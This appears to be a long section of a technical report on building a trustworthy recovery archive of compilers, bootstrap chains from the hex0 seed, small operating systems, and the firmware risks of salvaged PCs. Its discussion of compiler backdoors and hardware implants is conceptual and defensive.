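It is easy to overlook that a compiler may be descended from the trusted compiler used to test it. In Wheeler's first experiment, GCC had built the earliest copy of tcc and then served as the trusted compiler for testing it. That was enough to show that the method works, but a real test would need a trusted compiler that had never depended on GCC. Wheeler thinks an attacker would find it difficult to pass down an infection this way, since they would usually have to plan it before the new compiler was well known.

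As with old chips, a compiler's age is probably the best protection against tampering by a recent AI system. Human attackers in 1995 could have tampered with a compiler disc made that year, but they would have had to write a trigger for source code that did not exist yet. The archive's makers need evidence of the disc's age, so they should prefer original media and compare copies from several owners.

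Old compilers can be hard to compile. Intel's compiler could not easily compile three of the GCC versions that Wheeler considered, and the GCC on his own computer could not compile GCC 3.1.1. So the archive's makers may need to include a series of intermediate versions, each able to compile the next. They should test the whole series before sealing the archive.

Wheeler argues that defenders usually have an advantage because an attacker doesn't know in advance which compiler they will choose as the trusted one. An archive loses some of this advantage because its makers choose the compilers long before anyone runs the test. If the makers also publish the list of contents, an attacker can see which compilers to target. The makers could include more compilers than the test needs and let the rebuilders choose among them. The rebuilders could also write their own simple compiler, which no earlier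 attacker could have tampered with, or build one up from a seed small enough to check by hand.

None of this protects against changes to the source. Wheeler describes a "pop-up" attack, in which the attacker adds a self-copying backdoor to version 2 of a compiler's source and removes it from version 3. If version 2 built version 3, the binary of version 3 may be infected although its source is clean. People who read only versions 1 and 3 would miss the backdoor. Malicious source can also look innocent. In 2003, someone tried to add a backdoor to Linux with two lines of code that used "=" where a reader would expect "==". The developers caught it because their tools flagged a discrepancy. An adversary that can write good code might prefer this kind of attack to tampering with binaries, and the only defence is for people to read the source carefully.

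### What to store

For the toolchain, the archive therefore needs at least:

- **Two unrelated compilers**, as binaries that run on the stored or expected machines. At least one should predate the suspected adversary if the makers can find one that works.
- **The source of each compiler and of its parent**, with every version in between that helped to build it. This includes the assembler, linker and libraries, since a backdoor could be in any of them.
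- **Exact build instructions**, giving the versions, options, environment settings, directory names and order of steps. Someone who did not write the instructions should have followed them successfully, using only the archive.
- **The expected outputs**, including the intermediate files, so that rebuilders who get a different result can find the step at which it went wrong. Separate groups should produce these on different kinds of machine and agree on them before anyone seals the archive.

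The compressed source of GCC 3.0.4 is 18.4 megabytes, and the seven files in Wheeler's test add 7.9 megabytes. Together they would take up only about 24 frames of the archival film described earlier, at one bit per pixel. Reading that much source for hidden backdoors would be much harder than storing it, so at least one of the compilers should be small enough for a few people to read in full.

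## How small can the first program be, and what must follow it?

The bootstrappable project's compiler chain starts with hex0, a 357-byte program. People can check all of it by hand, so rebuilders who trust no compiler can start with hex0 and build one. But hex0 does almost nothing by itself, and getting from it to a modern compiler requires a lot of other source code, much of it decades old.

### What hex0 does

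Hex0 reads a text file, turns each pair of hexadecimal digits into a byte, and ignores anything on a line after a `#` or a `;`, so programmers can write comments there. GNU's *Stage0*, part of the manual for GNU Mes, shows these two lines from an early version of hex0's own source:

```
48 83 e8 30    # sub $0x30,%rax
c3             # ret
```

The comments give the same instructions in assembly language, which uses names instead of numbers. On a 64-bit x86 processor (the family in most PCs), `48 83 e8` means "subtract the next byte from the register rax". Here that byte is `30`, which is 48 in decimal. The instruction `c3` returns to the part of the program that needed the result. Computers store the characters 0 to 9 as the numbers 48 to 57, so subtracting 48 turns the character 7, stored as 55, into the number 7.

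When hex0 reads its own source, it produces a file identical to the running binary, which is why Guix counts the 357-byte binary as source code. Rebuilders must still check that the bytes match the hex digits in the source, which takes patience but no skill, and that the digits do what the comments claim. The second check requires a table of the processor's instructions, so the archive's printed layer should include one.

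The stored binary is optional because hex0's job is easy to do in other ways. Faase's *Verifying and documenting live-bootstrap* describes generating a replacement in Brainfuck, a deliberately awkward language with only eight commands. The replacement turned hex0's source into a file identical to the stored binary.

The small size also offers some protection. One reader argues in LWN's *Comments on "Pulling Linux up by its bootstraps"* (2024) that binaries this small are unlikely to contain a backdoor that can recognise a compiler and infect it.

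### From digits to a modern compiler

The next few programs take over the most tedious parts of writing in hex0. A program often has to jump to another place in its own code, and in hex0 the programmer must count the bytes to get there. live-bootstrap, a project that automates the whole build from the seeds to a working Linux system, documents the same jump in each of the first four languages:

```
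hex0    74 14
hex1    0F84 %b
hex2    74 !loop_options_done
M0      je %loop_options_done
```

All four mean "if the two values just compared were equal, jump to the end of the loop". In hex0, `14` is the distance, 20 bytes, and the programmer must recalculate it after adding or removing anything in between. Hex1 calculates the distance to a place the programmer has labelled with a single character. It always writes the distance as four bytes, so it needs `0F84`, a longer form of the instruction. Hex2 allows labels of any length. In M0, the programmer defines `je` as `0F84` once and can then use the name.

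The table shows live-bootstrap's main steps from there to a modern compiler.

| Program | Language of its source | What it adds |
|---|---|---|
| hex0 | hex0 | Turns digits into bytes |
| hex1 | hex0 | One-character labels |
| hex2 | hex1 | Long labels and more kinds of address |
| M0 | hex2 | Named instructions |
| cc_x86 | M0 | A limited subset of C |
| M2-Planet | The C that cc_x86 accepts | More of C, and output for several kinds of processor |
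| Mes | Simple C | An interpreter for Scheme, a dialect of Lisp |
| MesCC | Scheme | A C compiler good enough to build tcc |
| tcc | C | All of the 1989 C standard and most of the 1999 one |
| GCC 4.0.4 | C | An optimising C compiler |
| GCC 4.7.4 | C | C++ |
| GCC 10.4.0, then 13.1.0 | C++ | Modern C and C++ |

Programmers have to write the steps before M2-Planet separately for each kind of processor. From M2-Planet on, the same source code works for all of them, with small variations. Soon afterward, the build produces tools that unpack compressed files and calculate hashes, which are short values that change if any bit of a file changes. Rebuilders can then check the remaining source files against a printed list of hashes.

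Some rows of the table cover more than one build. live-bootstrap builds Mes with M2-Planet, then uses that copy to build a faster and less buggy one. MesCC compiles a version of tcc with 27 patches, and live-bootstrap recompiles it three times to add support for large integers and fractional numbers. live-bootstrap's developers chose GCC 4.7.4 because it is the last version written in C. Later versions need a C++ compiler, so rebuilders have to first build GCC 4.7.4 or something like it.

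### Starting without an operating system

The 357-byte hex0 is a Linux program, and it relies on Linux to open and save its files. Rebuilders who run it on an ordinary PC are therefore trusting the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system. live-bootstrap can remove this dependency by starting from the PC's firmware:

1. The firmware loads a tiny binary from the disk. This is the first stage of builder-hex0, and it contains a hex0 compiler. It reads the hex0 source of a small kernel, compiles it and runs it.
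2. The small kernel, builder-hex0's second stage, keeps files in memory and has its own simple command shell. It builds hex0 from source and runs the chain as far as tcc.
3. tcc compiles Fiwix, a clone of Linux 2.0 that is much simpler than Linux. Fiwix takes over and runs the build through the first GCC.
4. GCC compiles Linux 4.14, which takes over from Fiwix and runs everything else.

Rick Masters closed the last gap in the kernel bootstrap in May 2023 by adding a step in which Fiwix starts Linux (Masters 2023, *Complete the kernel bootstrap by adding kexec of Linux from Fiwix*). The developers use Linux 4.14 because newer versions need a more recent GCC. Linux 4.14 is still too big to build in one go under Fiwix, so they build it in two parts and delete the leftover files in between. The build can use only one processor core until Linux is running.

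Somebody also has to prepare the first disk, which the live-bootstrap project calls an unsolved problem because it can't be done without another computer. The disk must hold the tiny binary, the source of the small kernel, and every source file for the early steps, each preceded by its size and name. In Guix's *IRC channel logs* (2026), Andrius Štikonas, one of live-bootstrap's authors, says that people could in principle work out the contents by hand. The hard part is getting them into a modern computer, which has no row of switches or paper-tape reader. A punched-tape reader of the kind described earlier would therefore be useful even to rebuilders with plenty of PCs.

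The older stage0 project has a "monitor" program for machines with no operating system or firmware. It assembles hex0 as a person types it and saves the typed characters, so it also serves as a crude text editor. Rebuilders could use it to type in the next program, though a program as large as GCC would be impractical to type.

### What the sizes count

People quote several sizes for the seed, and they refer to different things.

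| Size | What it counts |
|---|---|
| 268 bytes | stage0's monitor, for typing programs in by hand |
| 280 bytes | Faase's figure for live-bootstrap's binary seed |
| 357 bytes | hex0 as a 32-bit x86 Linux program |
| About 25 MiB | Guile, the program that runs Guix's first builds |
| About 250 MB | All the binaries that Guix used to start from |

The smallest figure comes from stage0, whose instructions run the monitor on a virtual machine, so it is not the size of a program for a PC. The talk summary in Faase's *Reviewing live-bootstrap* (2025) gives 280 bytes without naming the files he counted. The 357 bytes include an 84-byte header that tells Linux how to load the file, leaving 273 for everything else. When live-bootstrap starts on an existing Linux system, it needs a second seed, kaem, a very simple shell that runs a list of commands. Live-bootstrap immediately rebuilds both seeds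 from source.

Guix has a much larger exception, a ready-made copy of the Scheme interpreter Guile. In 2023, Guix traced more than 22,000 software packages back to the 357-byte program, but the builds still ran under Guile, which is more than 70,000 times as large. Guile isn't one of the compilers in the chain, but it starts the builds and handles their files, so a malicious copy could alter them. GNU describes removing part of this dependency as the next priority. Linuxiac's *GNU Guix 1.5 Brings Plasma 6.5, GNOME 46, Rootless Mode, and More* reports that version 1.5 further reduced the prebuilt binaries that Guix needs. live-bootstrap doesn't use Guile until it has built its own copy, so it is the better choice for an archive meant to start from as little as possible.

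Shrinking hex0 further would achieve very little, because even a 100-byte version would need the same source code after it. That source code accounts for nearly all the reading and storage.

### Why the archive needs old software

A commenter on Hacker News counted 181 steps in live-bootstrap's description of the build. There are so many partly because the project has strict rules about what counts as source. Many packages include files that another program generated, such as a script that configures the build or C code produced from a language's grammar. These files are hard to read, and malicious code could hide in them. live-bootstrap deletes and regenerates them, so it must first build the programs that generate them.

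Perl, a programming language, shows what this involves. GCC and many other packages use a tool called Automake to generate their build files, and Automake is a Perl program. Perl itself is mostly C, but its source includes files that only Perl can generate. live-bootstrap gets round this in five steps:

1. It starts with Perl 5.000, which has the fewest generated files. The developers rewrote the two Perl scripts that make them in awk, a simpler language that the build already has.
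2. Perl 5.000 generates the files for 5.003.
3. Perl 5.003 does the same for 5.004_05, the last version it can build.
4. Perl 5.004_05 builds 5.005_03, again the last version it can manage.
5. Perl 5.005_03 builds 5.6.2, which is recent enough for the first GCC.

Two more versions come later. The build also uses eight versions of Python, from 2.0.1 to 3.11.1. The archive must hold the source of each version, and the patches and handwritten build files that make them work in this order. It also needs the packages that live-bootstrap normally downloads once it has a working network connection. The build doesn't need to download these if someone has put them on a second disk beforehand.

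Newer software tends to make the list longer. The Guix project points out that GCC began to require C++ in 2013 and that the GNU C library, which most Linux programs use, began to require Python in 2018. Both changes were convenient for people who already had a C++ compiler and Python.

An archive could avoid some of this by using a method that one of the LWN readers suggests, which is to run each package's configuration once, record the resulting compiler commands, and store them as a plain list. This would suit an archive because its software versions are fixed and its makers may know which machine the rebuilders will use. They could then leave out some of the configuration tools. The list would be a generated file, which live-bootstrap's rules are meant to exclude, but it would contain no logic and a person could read it line by line. If the rebuilders had a different machine, they would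 need the full set of tools to make a new list.

### How thoroughly has anyone checked the early steps?

Faase spent two years studying the early part of live-bootstrap to find out what it depends on. He first wrote a program that reads the build scripts and lists every command. He then wrote an x86 emulator with only the instructions the early programs use, which let him check hex0's code and look for other binaries the build might be using. The emulator was too slow to compile Mes. He also ran all the steps on a real Linux system and recorded the relevant requests the programs made to its kernel. From these records he produced a diagram and web pages that cover every program and source file up to the first tcc.

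In *Show HN*, fjfaase says the first 19 steps run over 700 executables and improvements could cut this by at least half. His review identifies the files that reviewers have to read. The review is weaker evidence that those files are harmless, because one person did most of the work and a careful author could have hidden something from him. He found bugs in M2-Mesoplanet, one of the early compiler tools, which suggests that few people had used it outside the build.

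He also thinks Mes is more than the job requires. MesCC runs inside an interpreter and reloads all its Scheme files for every C file it compiles. A developer of StageX, another Linux distribution that uses the chain, says in the same discussion that Mes takes longer to build than anything else in the distribution except Rust. Few people maintain Mes. Nieuwenhuizen (2025), in *GNU Mes 0.27.1 released*, reports 53 changes by four people in a year.

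### Shorter paths

Faase's C compiler, which replaces Mes, made a much faster build possible. In June 2026 a programmer known as stabbles announced shpack in Guix's logs. It builds GCC 4.7 from the usual seeds in two and a half minutes on 64-bit x86 and 64-bit ARM processors. Three days later, according to the logs, it could build GCC 16, with a recent GNU C library, in under 30 minutes.

shpack is fast partly because it attempts less. It needs a running Linux kernel, and it includes some generated C files that its author considers trivial. He wrote it for people who use supercomputers they don't control and who have to trust the kernel anyway. Another developer, Alexandre Gaigalas, suggested a way to get the benefits of both approaches: someone builds everything from the firmware up, kernel included, and publishes the hashes, and others use the quicker method and compare their results. This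 would work only if the two methods built identical files, so the archive's makers would have to settle on the same versions and options for both.

Zakaria's *A C++ toolchain from 357 bytes, in Bazel* describes another path, for Google's build system, Bazel. It passes through Mes, tcc, GCC 4.6.4 and GCC 10.4.0 to Clang 22, the main alternative to GCC. Zakaria then used Clang to compile two widely used C++ libraries without changing them, and all 236 tests he ran passed. This is good evidence that the compiler works, but a compiler with a backdoor could pass the same tests.

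His build also lists every program it ran but did not build. There are only two, the hex0 seed and bash, the shell on his own machine. An archive's makers should want such a list for every build, because it would show them what they had forgotten to include. The remedy for bash is simple in principle, since live-bootstrap builds a copy from source.

Zakaria finished the project with the help of a large language model, and says the remaining steps were mechanical. Faase mentions in Guix's logs that a contributor used Claude Code, Anthropic's programming tool, to extend his compiler to 64-bit processors. This matters little for most users, but if an archive is meant for recovery from a hostile AI system, its makers have a reason to read such contributions more closely, or to store an older version of the chain as well.

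Some programmers have asked why the chain doesn't use Forth, a language whose smallest versions fit in 512 bytes. Jeremiah Orians, who created hex0, answered on LWN that the project had bootstrapped several Forths, but none yet led to Linux and GCC. Dupras took up this work for Collapse OS. Rebuilders who could manage without Linux and GCC would have far less source to store and read.

### Which processors does it work on?

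In mid-2026 only 32-bit x86 had the complete chain, from firmware to a modern compiler. Most 64-bit PCs can run 32-bit x86 programs too.

| Processor | Starting from firmware | Starting on Linux |
|---|---|---|
| 32-bit x86 | The whole chain, to GCC 13 | The whole chain |
| 64-bit x86 | Early tools, up to M2-Planet | GCC 4.7 and later |
| 64-bit ARM | Early tools, up to M2-Planet | GCC 4.7 |
| 64-bit RISC-V | Early tools, up to M2-Planet | Early tools, with later steps in progress |

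The early tools in the second column come from abuild, a hobby project by Gaigalas. It also makes its own first disk image, almost entirely with tools from the chain. The next obstacle is the kernel in the middle. In Guix's logs, Gaigalas calls it a "hard wall" for ARM and RISC-V, because someone would have to adapt Fiwix or an old version of Linux to those processors, or write a new kernel.

The old versions of GCC that a bootstrap depends on can't produce RISC-V programs, because GCC did not support RISC-V until after it had begun to require C++. A developer has added RISC-V support to GCC 4.6.5. Until the rest of the chain works for RISC-V, rebuilders who want a RISC-V computer on an FPGA, like Somlo's, will need to run the bootstrap on an x86 PC and use the resulting compiler to produce programs for the new machine. An archive that depends on this chain should include an x86 PC, or its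 makers should be confident that the rebuilders can find one.

### Bootstrapping and diverse double-compiling

Diverse double-compiling tests a compiler binary that somebody already has. Bootstrapping makes a new one without using any existing compiler. In the notation of the previous section, a bootstrap starts with a seed b₀ and repeats

bᵢ = c(sᵢ, bᵢ₋₁)

until it produces the compiler bₙ. (In practice, one step may use several earlier programs.) An infected copy of GCC can't pass a backdoor to bₙ, because no existing copy of GCC takes part. In return, the rebuilders have to trust every source from s₁ to sₙ. Wheeler's test needs a trusted compiler, but the only source code it compiles is that of the suspect and its parent.

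The longer list matters because reviewers make mistakes. Suppose, for illustration, that each of the 181 steps has a 1 in 1,000 chance of containing malicious source that the reviewers missed. The chance that at least one of them does is 1 − 0.999¹⁸¹, or about 17%. According to a comment on LWN, an attacker hid a backdoor in xz, a compression program, by putting part of it in a test file that looked like deliberately damaged data and part in a build script that appeared in the released package but not in the public repository. live-bootstrap's rule against generated files would help with some attacks of this kind. The archive's makers should also compare each released package with its repository.

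The two methods work well together because a freshly bootstrapped compiler has no binary ancestor in common with the compiler under suspicion, which makes it a good choice for the trusted compiler in Wheeler's test. The rebuilders can also run the whole bootstrap on several machines and compare the results, as one of live-bootstrap's authors proposes on LWN. Another reader recommends using processors from different makers, firmware and disks of different origins, and computers of very different ages. That reader also wants several routes through the old versions of GCC to give the same result, so that a backdoor in one version would show up as a difference. Volunteers made a similar comparison on a small scale in 2019, when they built the Mes compiler on three Linux distributions and got identical files.

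Neither method removes the need to trust the processor and firmware, or the kernel if the build starts on one. An LWN reader argues that an attacker only has to recognise files that contain programs. This answers another reader's argument that Thompson's attack can't work against every possible compiler because no program can recognise them all. Program files are easy to recognise on Linux because their header starts with the bytes `7F 45 4C 46`, as Debian's *elf32.hex2* shows. A malicious kernel could look for those bytes and add a backdoor to each new program as the build saves it, and hex0's small size wouldn't prevent this. Comparing results from different machines would expose the change unless every machine made the same one.

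For this reason a third reader doubts that bootstrapping adds much practical security, since people already have more reason to trust GCC than the firmware beneath it. The live-bootstrap author replies that he has learned from the project how fragile the software supply chain is, and that he isn't convinced firmware is much worse. For an archive, the objection is strongest if rebuilders have to use salvaged machines. If they have clean stored machines, they already trust the hardware, so the compiler may be the part they have most reason to doubt.

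Gaigalas (2026) argues in *Bootstrapping Is Not Security Paranoia* that bootstrapping can't provide complete certainty about security, because people have to trust the hardware at some point. He thinks its main benefit is that it forces developers to make every dependency explicit. live-bootstrap's developers repeatedly found that tools which supposedly needed only a C compiler also relied on the behaviour of a particular shell, a certain directory layout, or other undocumented features of the machine.

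He is writing for ordinary software developers, but the argument is stronger for a recovery archive. A developer who finds a file missing can download it. Rebuilders can't, so one missing file might stop the chain at step 40 of 181. If the archive's makers can complete the bootstrap on a disconnected machine, using only what they plan to store, they will know that the archive's software is closed in the sense defined earlier. This test would be worth doing even if they fully trusted their compilers.

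## Which operating system should be stored?

Linux is a candidate because the bootstrap ends with a modern compiler running on it. However, it is far too large for a small group to read, and it can't run on the simplest machines that rebuilders might have to make. Programmers have written much smaller systems, including two designed for use after a collapse.

Whichever system the archive holds, rebuilders need it to do six jobs:

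- save and load data on whatever disks or memory chips they have
- edit text
- compile or assemble programs
- operate the keyboard, display and other devices
- copy itself to another machine
- program microcontrollers

The last job is loading programs into microcontrollers, which requires another computer. Microcontrollers run battery chargers, pumps and factory equipment. Dupras cares about this job most. On the Collapse OS website, he agrees that a simpler society would have much less information to process, but says he wants to save electronics rather than computing.

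### Two systems for two stages of collapse

Dupras divides a collapse into two stages and wrote an operating system for each. Dusk OS is for the first stage, when the global supply chain has broken and nobody can make modern computers, but many still work. Collapse OS is for the second, which begins in each community when its last modern computer stops working. Dupras personally expects the supply chain to break before 2030, but the distinction is useful whatever the date.

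In the second stage, people would build computers from salvaged chips. Dupras thinks 8-bit chips suit this best, partly because more of them have pins that go through holes in a board, so people can wire them by hand. Most modern chips sit flat on a board made specially for them. He also thinks people with simple tools could more easily make one working machine from two broken Sega Master Systems, which are 1980s games consoles, than from two broken laptops.

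Collapse OS is tiny. According to Collapse OS's *Why Forth?*, the first version, in Z80 assembly language, could assemble itself using a 5 KB shell, a 5 KB assembler and 8 KB of memory. Dupras then rewrote it in Forth, a language in which programmers define new commands, called words, from existing ones. For example:

```
: double dup + ;
```

This defines a word that copies a number and adds the two copies, so `5 double` gives 10. Only a few basic words have to be machine code, so a much simpler assembler can build them. The Forth version therefore needs about the same resources as the old one but offers a more powerful language.

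Such a small system is inconvenient to use. It stores text in blocks of 16 lines of 64 characters and can't display its own documentation. In the Collapse OS manual, Dupras expects each community to print the documentation before its last modern computer stops working. He recommends learning Forth from Leo Brodie's book *Starting Forth* and warns that doing without the book could be "a rough ride". The archive's printed layer should include both the documentation and Brodie's book.

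Dusk OS is a larger Forth system for more modern machines. According to its website, it starts from a core of about 1,000 lines of assembly and compiles the rest of itself from source every time the computer starts. The rest includes a compiler for what Dupras calls "almost C", so that people can adapt existing C programs instead of rewriting them. When he compared it with GCC on a short program that finds prime numbers, the Dusk version took 1.23 seconds, against 1.22 for GCC without optimisation and 0.46 with it. That is impressive for such a small compiler, but it is only one program, and Dupras chose it himself.

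The C compiler in version 32 of Dusk OS has 38 KB of source, according to a size count on the Dusk OS website, compared with 1,420 KB for the more complete tcc. The whole system has 930 KB of source, excluding documentation and tests. At 30 characters a line, that is about 31,000 lines, or 520 printed pages. Permacomputing's *Dusk OS* gives only about 10,000 lines, probably for an earlier version.

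### A system that fits in a book

In 1985 Niklaus Wirth and Jürg Gutknecht, computer scientists from ETH Zürich, were on sabbatical at a laboratory in California, where Gutknecht had to write a compiler for an advanced workstation. The workstation's operating system kept failing, and the two men found it nearly impossible to study. It had little documentation, so they interviewed its designers, but often could not understand the answers. Rebuilders would be worse off because they would have no designers to ask.

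Wirth and Gutknecht decided to write a system that people could understand as a whole, and they explain it in a single book, *Project Oberon* (2013), with program listings. The compiler has fewer than 2,900 lines and compiles itself in about three seconds. The entire system compiles itself in under ten seconds and, with its compiler, fits easily in 1 MB of memory. It runs on a simple processor that Wirth designed for an FPGA and describes in the same book. The 1992 edition left out the parts written in assembly language. Wirth later rewrote these in Oberon, the project's own programming language, which let him include them.

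Wirth also argued in 2013 that the complexity of popular operating systems gives outsiders opportunities to add back doors unnoticed, and that the only safe remedy is to build a new system from scratch.

The Project Oberon (2021) website claims that one person can know and implement the whole system. The original work is weak evidence for this because its two authors were experts working on their own design. Dupras provides better evidence because he had no part in designing Oberon, though he is an unusually capable programmer. He has ported the Oberon system to Dusk OS, and in the discussion under AlexeyBrin's *OBNC* (2025), a forum post about another Oberon compiler, he says that his own compiler for the language takes less than 1,500 lines of Forth.

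### Fiwix and Linux From Scratch

Rebuilders who want to run existing software will need something closer to Linux. Fiwix, the small kernel that live-bootstrap uses partway through its build, is also the basis of a complete operating system, FiwixOS. The kernel's developer keeps its code, which is under 50,000 lines, simple for students, and it works with many existing GNU programs. He compiled every package in FiwixOS 3.5 on FiwixOS itself. The system needs a 386 processor with floating-point hardware and 4 MB of memory, or 16 MB to install, according to Fiwix (2025). The same release notes warn that a few bugs can crash the kernel and that files occasionally become corrupted, and recommend regular disk checks and backups.

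People would have to read more than the kernel. Dupras counts 80,000 lines for the C compiler tcc and 190,000 for Busybox, a compact collection of everyday commands. With the Fiwix kernel, a minimal Unix-like system that can compile C comes to about 320,000 lines.

For full Linux, the archive could include the instructions in *Linux From Scratch* (Beekmans, 2026), a free book that takes readers through building a system from source. It covers more than 70 packages and gives a reason for each. For example, the kernel's build needs the calculator program Bc, and the manual-page viewer needs a database library that nothing else in the book uses. The finished system includes everything needed to build another copy of itself. In a test of an earlier edition, the build took about four hours on a four-core PC.

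The book is written for readers who already know how to use the command line and install Linux software, so the archive needs a beginner's guide too. The book's instructions also require a running Linux system to start from. live-bootstrap can supply one, but the archive's makers should test whether its old 4.14 kernel is recent enough, and add an intermediate step if it isn't.

The table compares the five systems, mostly using the projects' own figures.

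| System | Processors | Size and memory | Existing software |
|---|---|---|---|
| Collapse OS | Z80, 6502, 6809, 8086 | About 10 KB of programs and 8 KB of memory to assemble itself | Very little |
| Dusk OS | 32-bit and 64-bit x86, ARM, RISC-V, Motorola 68000 family | 930 KB of source | C programs, once someone adapts them |
| Project Oberon | Wirth's own design, with other versions for x86 and ARM | Compiler under 2,900 lines; runs in 1 MB | Programs written in Oberon |
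| Fiwix | 32-bit x86 | Kernel under 50,000 lines; 4 MB, or 16 MB to install | Many GNU programs |
| Linux From Scratch | 32-bit and 64-bit x86; ARM and PowerPC with changes | 3.6 to 4.4 GB to build | Most open-source software |

### The driver problem

An operating system is useless on a machine whose disk it can't read. The processor communicates with a disk through a controller, a chip with registers that the processor can write numbers to. To read from the disk, the kernel writes a location and a "read" command to the right registers, waits, and copies the data into memory. Different kinds of controller use different registers and commands, so the kernel needs a driver, which is code written for the kind of controller in that machine.

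Suppose rebuilders try to start Fiwix on a salvaged ten-year-old PC. Its disk controller uses AHCI, a common interface for SATA disks.

1. The PC's firmware has its own code for reading the disk, and uses it to load the kernel into memory.
2. The kernel starts and takes control of the hardware.
3. The kernel now needs the rest of the operating system, which is still on the disk. Fiwix's *Features* lists a driver for the older IDE/ATA disks but none for AHCI, so the startup fails.
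4. The rebuilders can't use a USB disk or fetch the files from another machine, because version 1.7.0 has no USB or network support.

People could understand every line of Fiwix and still be unable to connect their computers to a network. Fiwix (2026) announced in September that the next version will include networking, but its only driver for a physical network card is for the RTL8139, so it won't help people with a different card.

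Rebuilders could get round the problem on some PCs by changing a firmware setting so that the disk controller behaves like an older one. They could also load the whole system into memory at the start and treat part of the memory as a disk. TinkerOS, a modified version of the hobby operating system TempleOS, can run this way on machines whose drives it doesn't support. Fiwix can use memory as a disk too, but people would lose their work when they turned the machine off unless they could save it elsewhere, perhaps over a serial cable.

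The lasting solution is to write the missing driver, which requires the controller's documentation. Some manufacturers don't publish it. OpenBSD, for instance, advises users to avoid Nvidia graphics cards because the company resists releasing the information that driver writers need. Rebuilders would also have to write and test the driver on a machine that already works.

Linux is large partly because it has drivers for so many devices. In TU Wien's *Almost native Gforth*, the Linux kernel operates the hardware and Forth is the only program that runs on top of it. This system needs 8 MB of memory and is simple to work in, but people still have to trust the Linux kernel.

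Linux does not support everything either. One recent ARM laptop needs a file describing that particular model before it can run Linux (Debian Wiki, *Debian on Lenovo T14s Gen6 Snapdragon*). New kernels can also drop support for old machines, as Linux 7.1 did for the 486 processor (Proven, 2026, *Linux kernel 7.1 sends Intel 486 support to silicon heaven*). An archive meant for salvaged machines should therefore hold both an old and a new kernel.

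Storing clean machines largely avoids the driver problem, because the archive's makers can choose the computer and the operating system together. They should test every disk, keyboard and network card they store, including the spares.

### Would ordinary copies of Linux survive?

Many readers think small systems like Dupras's solve a problem nobody will have. In comments on OSNews, one predicts that people would keep using Windows XP or whatever else still ran on their hardware. Another expects survivors to find 64-bit laptops from the 2010s rather than 32-bit PCs from the 1990s, and recommends Debian, a Linux distribution that runs on almost anything.

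Dupras accepts part of this. He tells people without technical skills that they should "just use Linux and hope for the best". He also says that his project matters only if the collapse is severe enough that people can't maintain modern technology, but not so severe that they have more urgent concerns. The point about 64-bit laptops is weaker now that Dusk OS has a version for 64-bit x86.

Collapse OS still supports few machines, but Dupras says people can adapt it themselves. Its *Bootstrap guide* divides the system into five layers, some of which stay the same on every processor. Someone with an unsupported machine must supply the startup code, the basic words for its processor and the drivers. Dupras calls this "pretty hairy stuff" and wants communities to start on it while they still have modern computers.

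The lack of software is a stronger objection to Collapse OS than to Dusk OS, which Dupras says is meant to run existing applications rather than new ones. Somebody still has to adapt each application, though.

In *Collapse OS - An OS Created to Run After the World Ends*, John Paul Wohlscheid asks how anyone would get the system once GitHub was down, and doubts that more than a handful of people could build a computer for it from scavenged parts. Storing a copy in the archive solves the first problem. The second is still a serious concern, and Dupras told VICE that very few people had both the skills and the outlook to help him develop Collapse OS.

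The strength of these objections depends on the disaster. After a war or an economic collapse, millions of good copies of Linux would survive, and most people should use them. If a hostile AI had reached the machines holding those copies, they would be as suspect as everything else on the machines, though copies on old discs that had stayed offline would not be. Rebuilders would then have a much better reason to want a system they could read.

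### Small enough to read, or large enough to use

People who compile Linux from source can't in practice audit all of it, though Beekmans argues that they are free to. At 1,000 lines a day, one person could read the Oberon compiler in three days and the Fiwix kernel in 50, but 20 million lines of Linux would take 55 years. Rebuilders could leave out most of those lines, which are for hardware they don't have, but the rest would still be very large, and the kernel is only one of the packages.

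Line counts also make Forth code look easier to understand than it is. Dupras admits that Forth is hard to read because readers have to keep more in their heads than with other languages. He often finds it easier to rewrite a Forth word than to work out how he wrote it.

The large system is necessary because rebuilders must eventually design new computers. Somlo's FPGA computer, which has 512 MB of memory, builds its own bitstream with open-source tools that run on Linux. Collapse OS could never run such tools. Dusk OS might run some of them one day, but much engineering software is written in C++, which its compiler doesn't support.

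The archive should therefore hold at least one system of each kind. Rebuilders could use the small one to edit files, write firmware into chips, program microcontrollers and check the hashes of the larger system's files before running any of them. They would still have to trust the firmware that the small system runs on. Live-bootstrap needs a starting disk that nobody can yet prepare without another computer. An improvised machine running Collapse OS might be able to make that disk, because Collapse OS can edit binary data and write to storage devices. The archive's makers should test this before relying on it.

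The best small system depends on the hardware. Dusk OS suits salvaged PCs, Project Oberon suits a new computer built on an FPGA, and Collapse OS suits 8-bit machines. The source code of all three would take up only a few megabytes, so the archive can easily include them all. Learning them takes far more effort than storing them, so the people who will use the archive should practise on at least one beforehand.

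## Can salvaged computers be trusted to run the archive?

Rebuilders can make good use of salvaged computers, but wiping the disk and installing a clean operating system isn't enough to make one safe. An ordinary PC has several small processors besides the main one, and many of them run firmware that an intruder could have changed. Rebuilders can replace some of this firmware with simple tools, but they can't even read the firmware in other parts.

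### Where the changeable code is

A PC's startup firmware is stored in a flash memory chip on the motherboard, and on most PCs since about 2012 it follows a standard called UEFI. The firmware loads a boot program from the disk, which then loads the operating system. Malicious code implanted in the firmware therefore runs before anything the rebuilders install and can tamper with the new system at every start.

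Many PCs also have a management processor, a small separate computer that helps start the machine and lets administrators control it remotely. The main processor has its own changeable code, called microcode, which breaks complicated instructions into simpler steps.

| Location | Does reinstalling the operating system remove an implant? | Can people read it from outside? | Can they rewrite it? |
|---|---|---|---|
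| Boot files on the disk | Only if they wipe the whole disk | Yes, on another computer | Yes |
| UEFI flash | No | Usually, with a device attached to the chip | Usually |
| Management processor | No | In part, since some of its code is often in the UEFI flash | In part, and often only with code the manufacturer has signed |
| Disk or SSD controller | No | Rarely in full | Often, but not always completely |
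| Network card | No | Yes, if it has a separate flash chip | Usually, if it has a separate flash chip |
| USB device | No | Rarely | Depends on the controller |
| Processor microcode | Updates vanish at power-off, but the UEFI firmware may reload them | Not the built-in part | Only temporarily, with signed updates |

The damage a compromised part can do depends on how it connects to the rest of the machine. Network cards and the fastest SSDs can often read and write main memory directly, so an implant in one could change a compiler while it runs. A disk on an ordinary SATA cable can change only the data that passes through it. A USB keyboard can send only keystrokes, but these can include harmful commands.

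### Implants found in disks and USB devices

The best-known disk implant came from attackers whom the Russian security company Kaspersky named the Equation Group. According to Kaspersky's *Equation Group* (2015), their malware could replace the firmware of 12 categories of hard disk and SSD, including models from most of the large manufacturers. The new firmware survived formatting the disk and reinstalling the operating system, and gave the attackers a hidden storage area. Kaspersky discovered this from the group's Windows malware, where it found two versions of the module that rewrote the firmware, apparently compiled in 2010 and 2013. It identified only a few victims targeted with the module.

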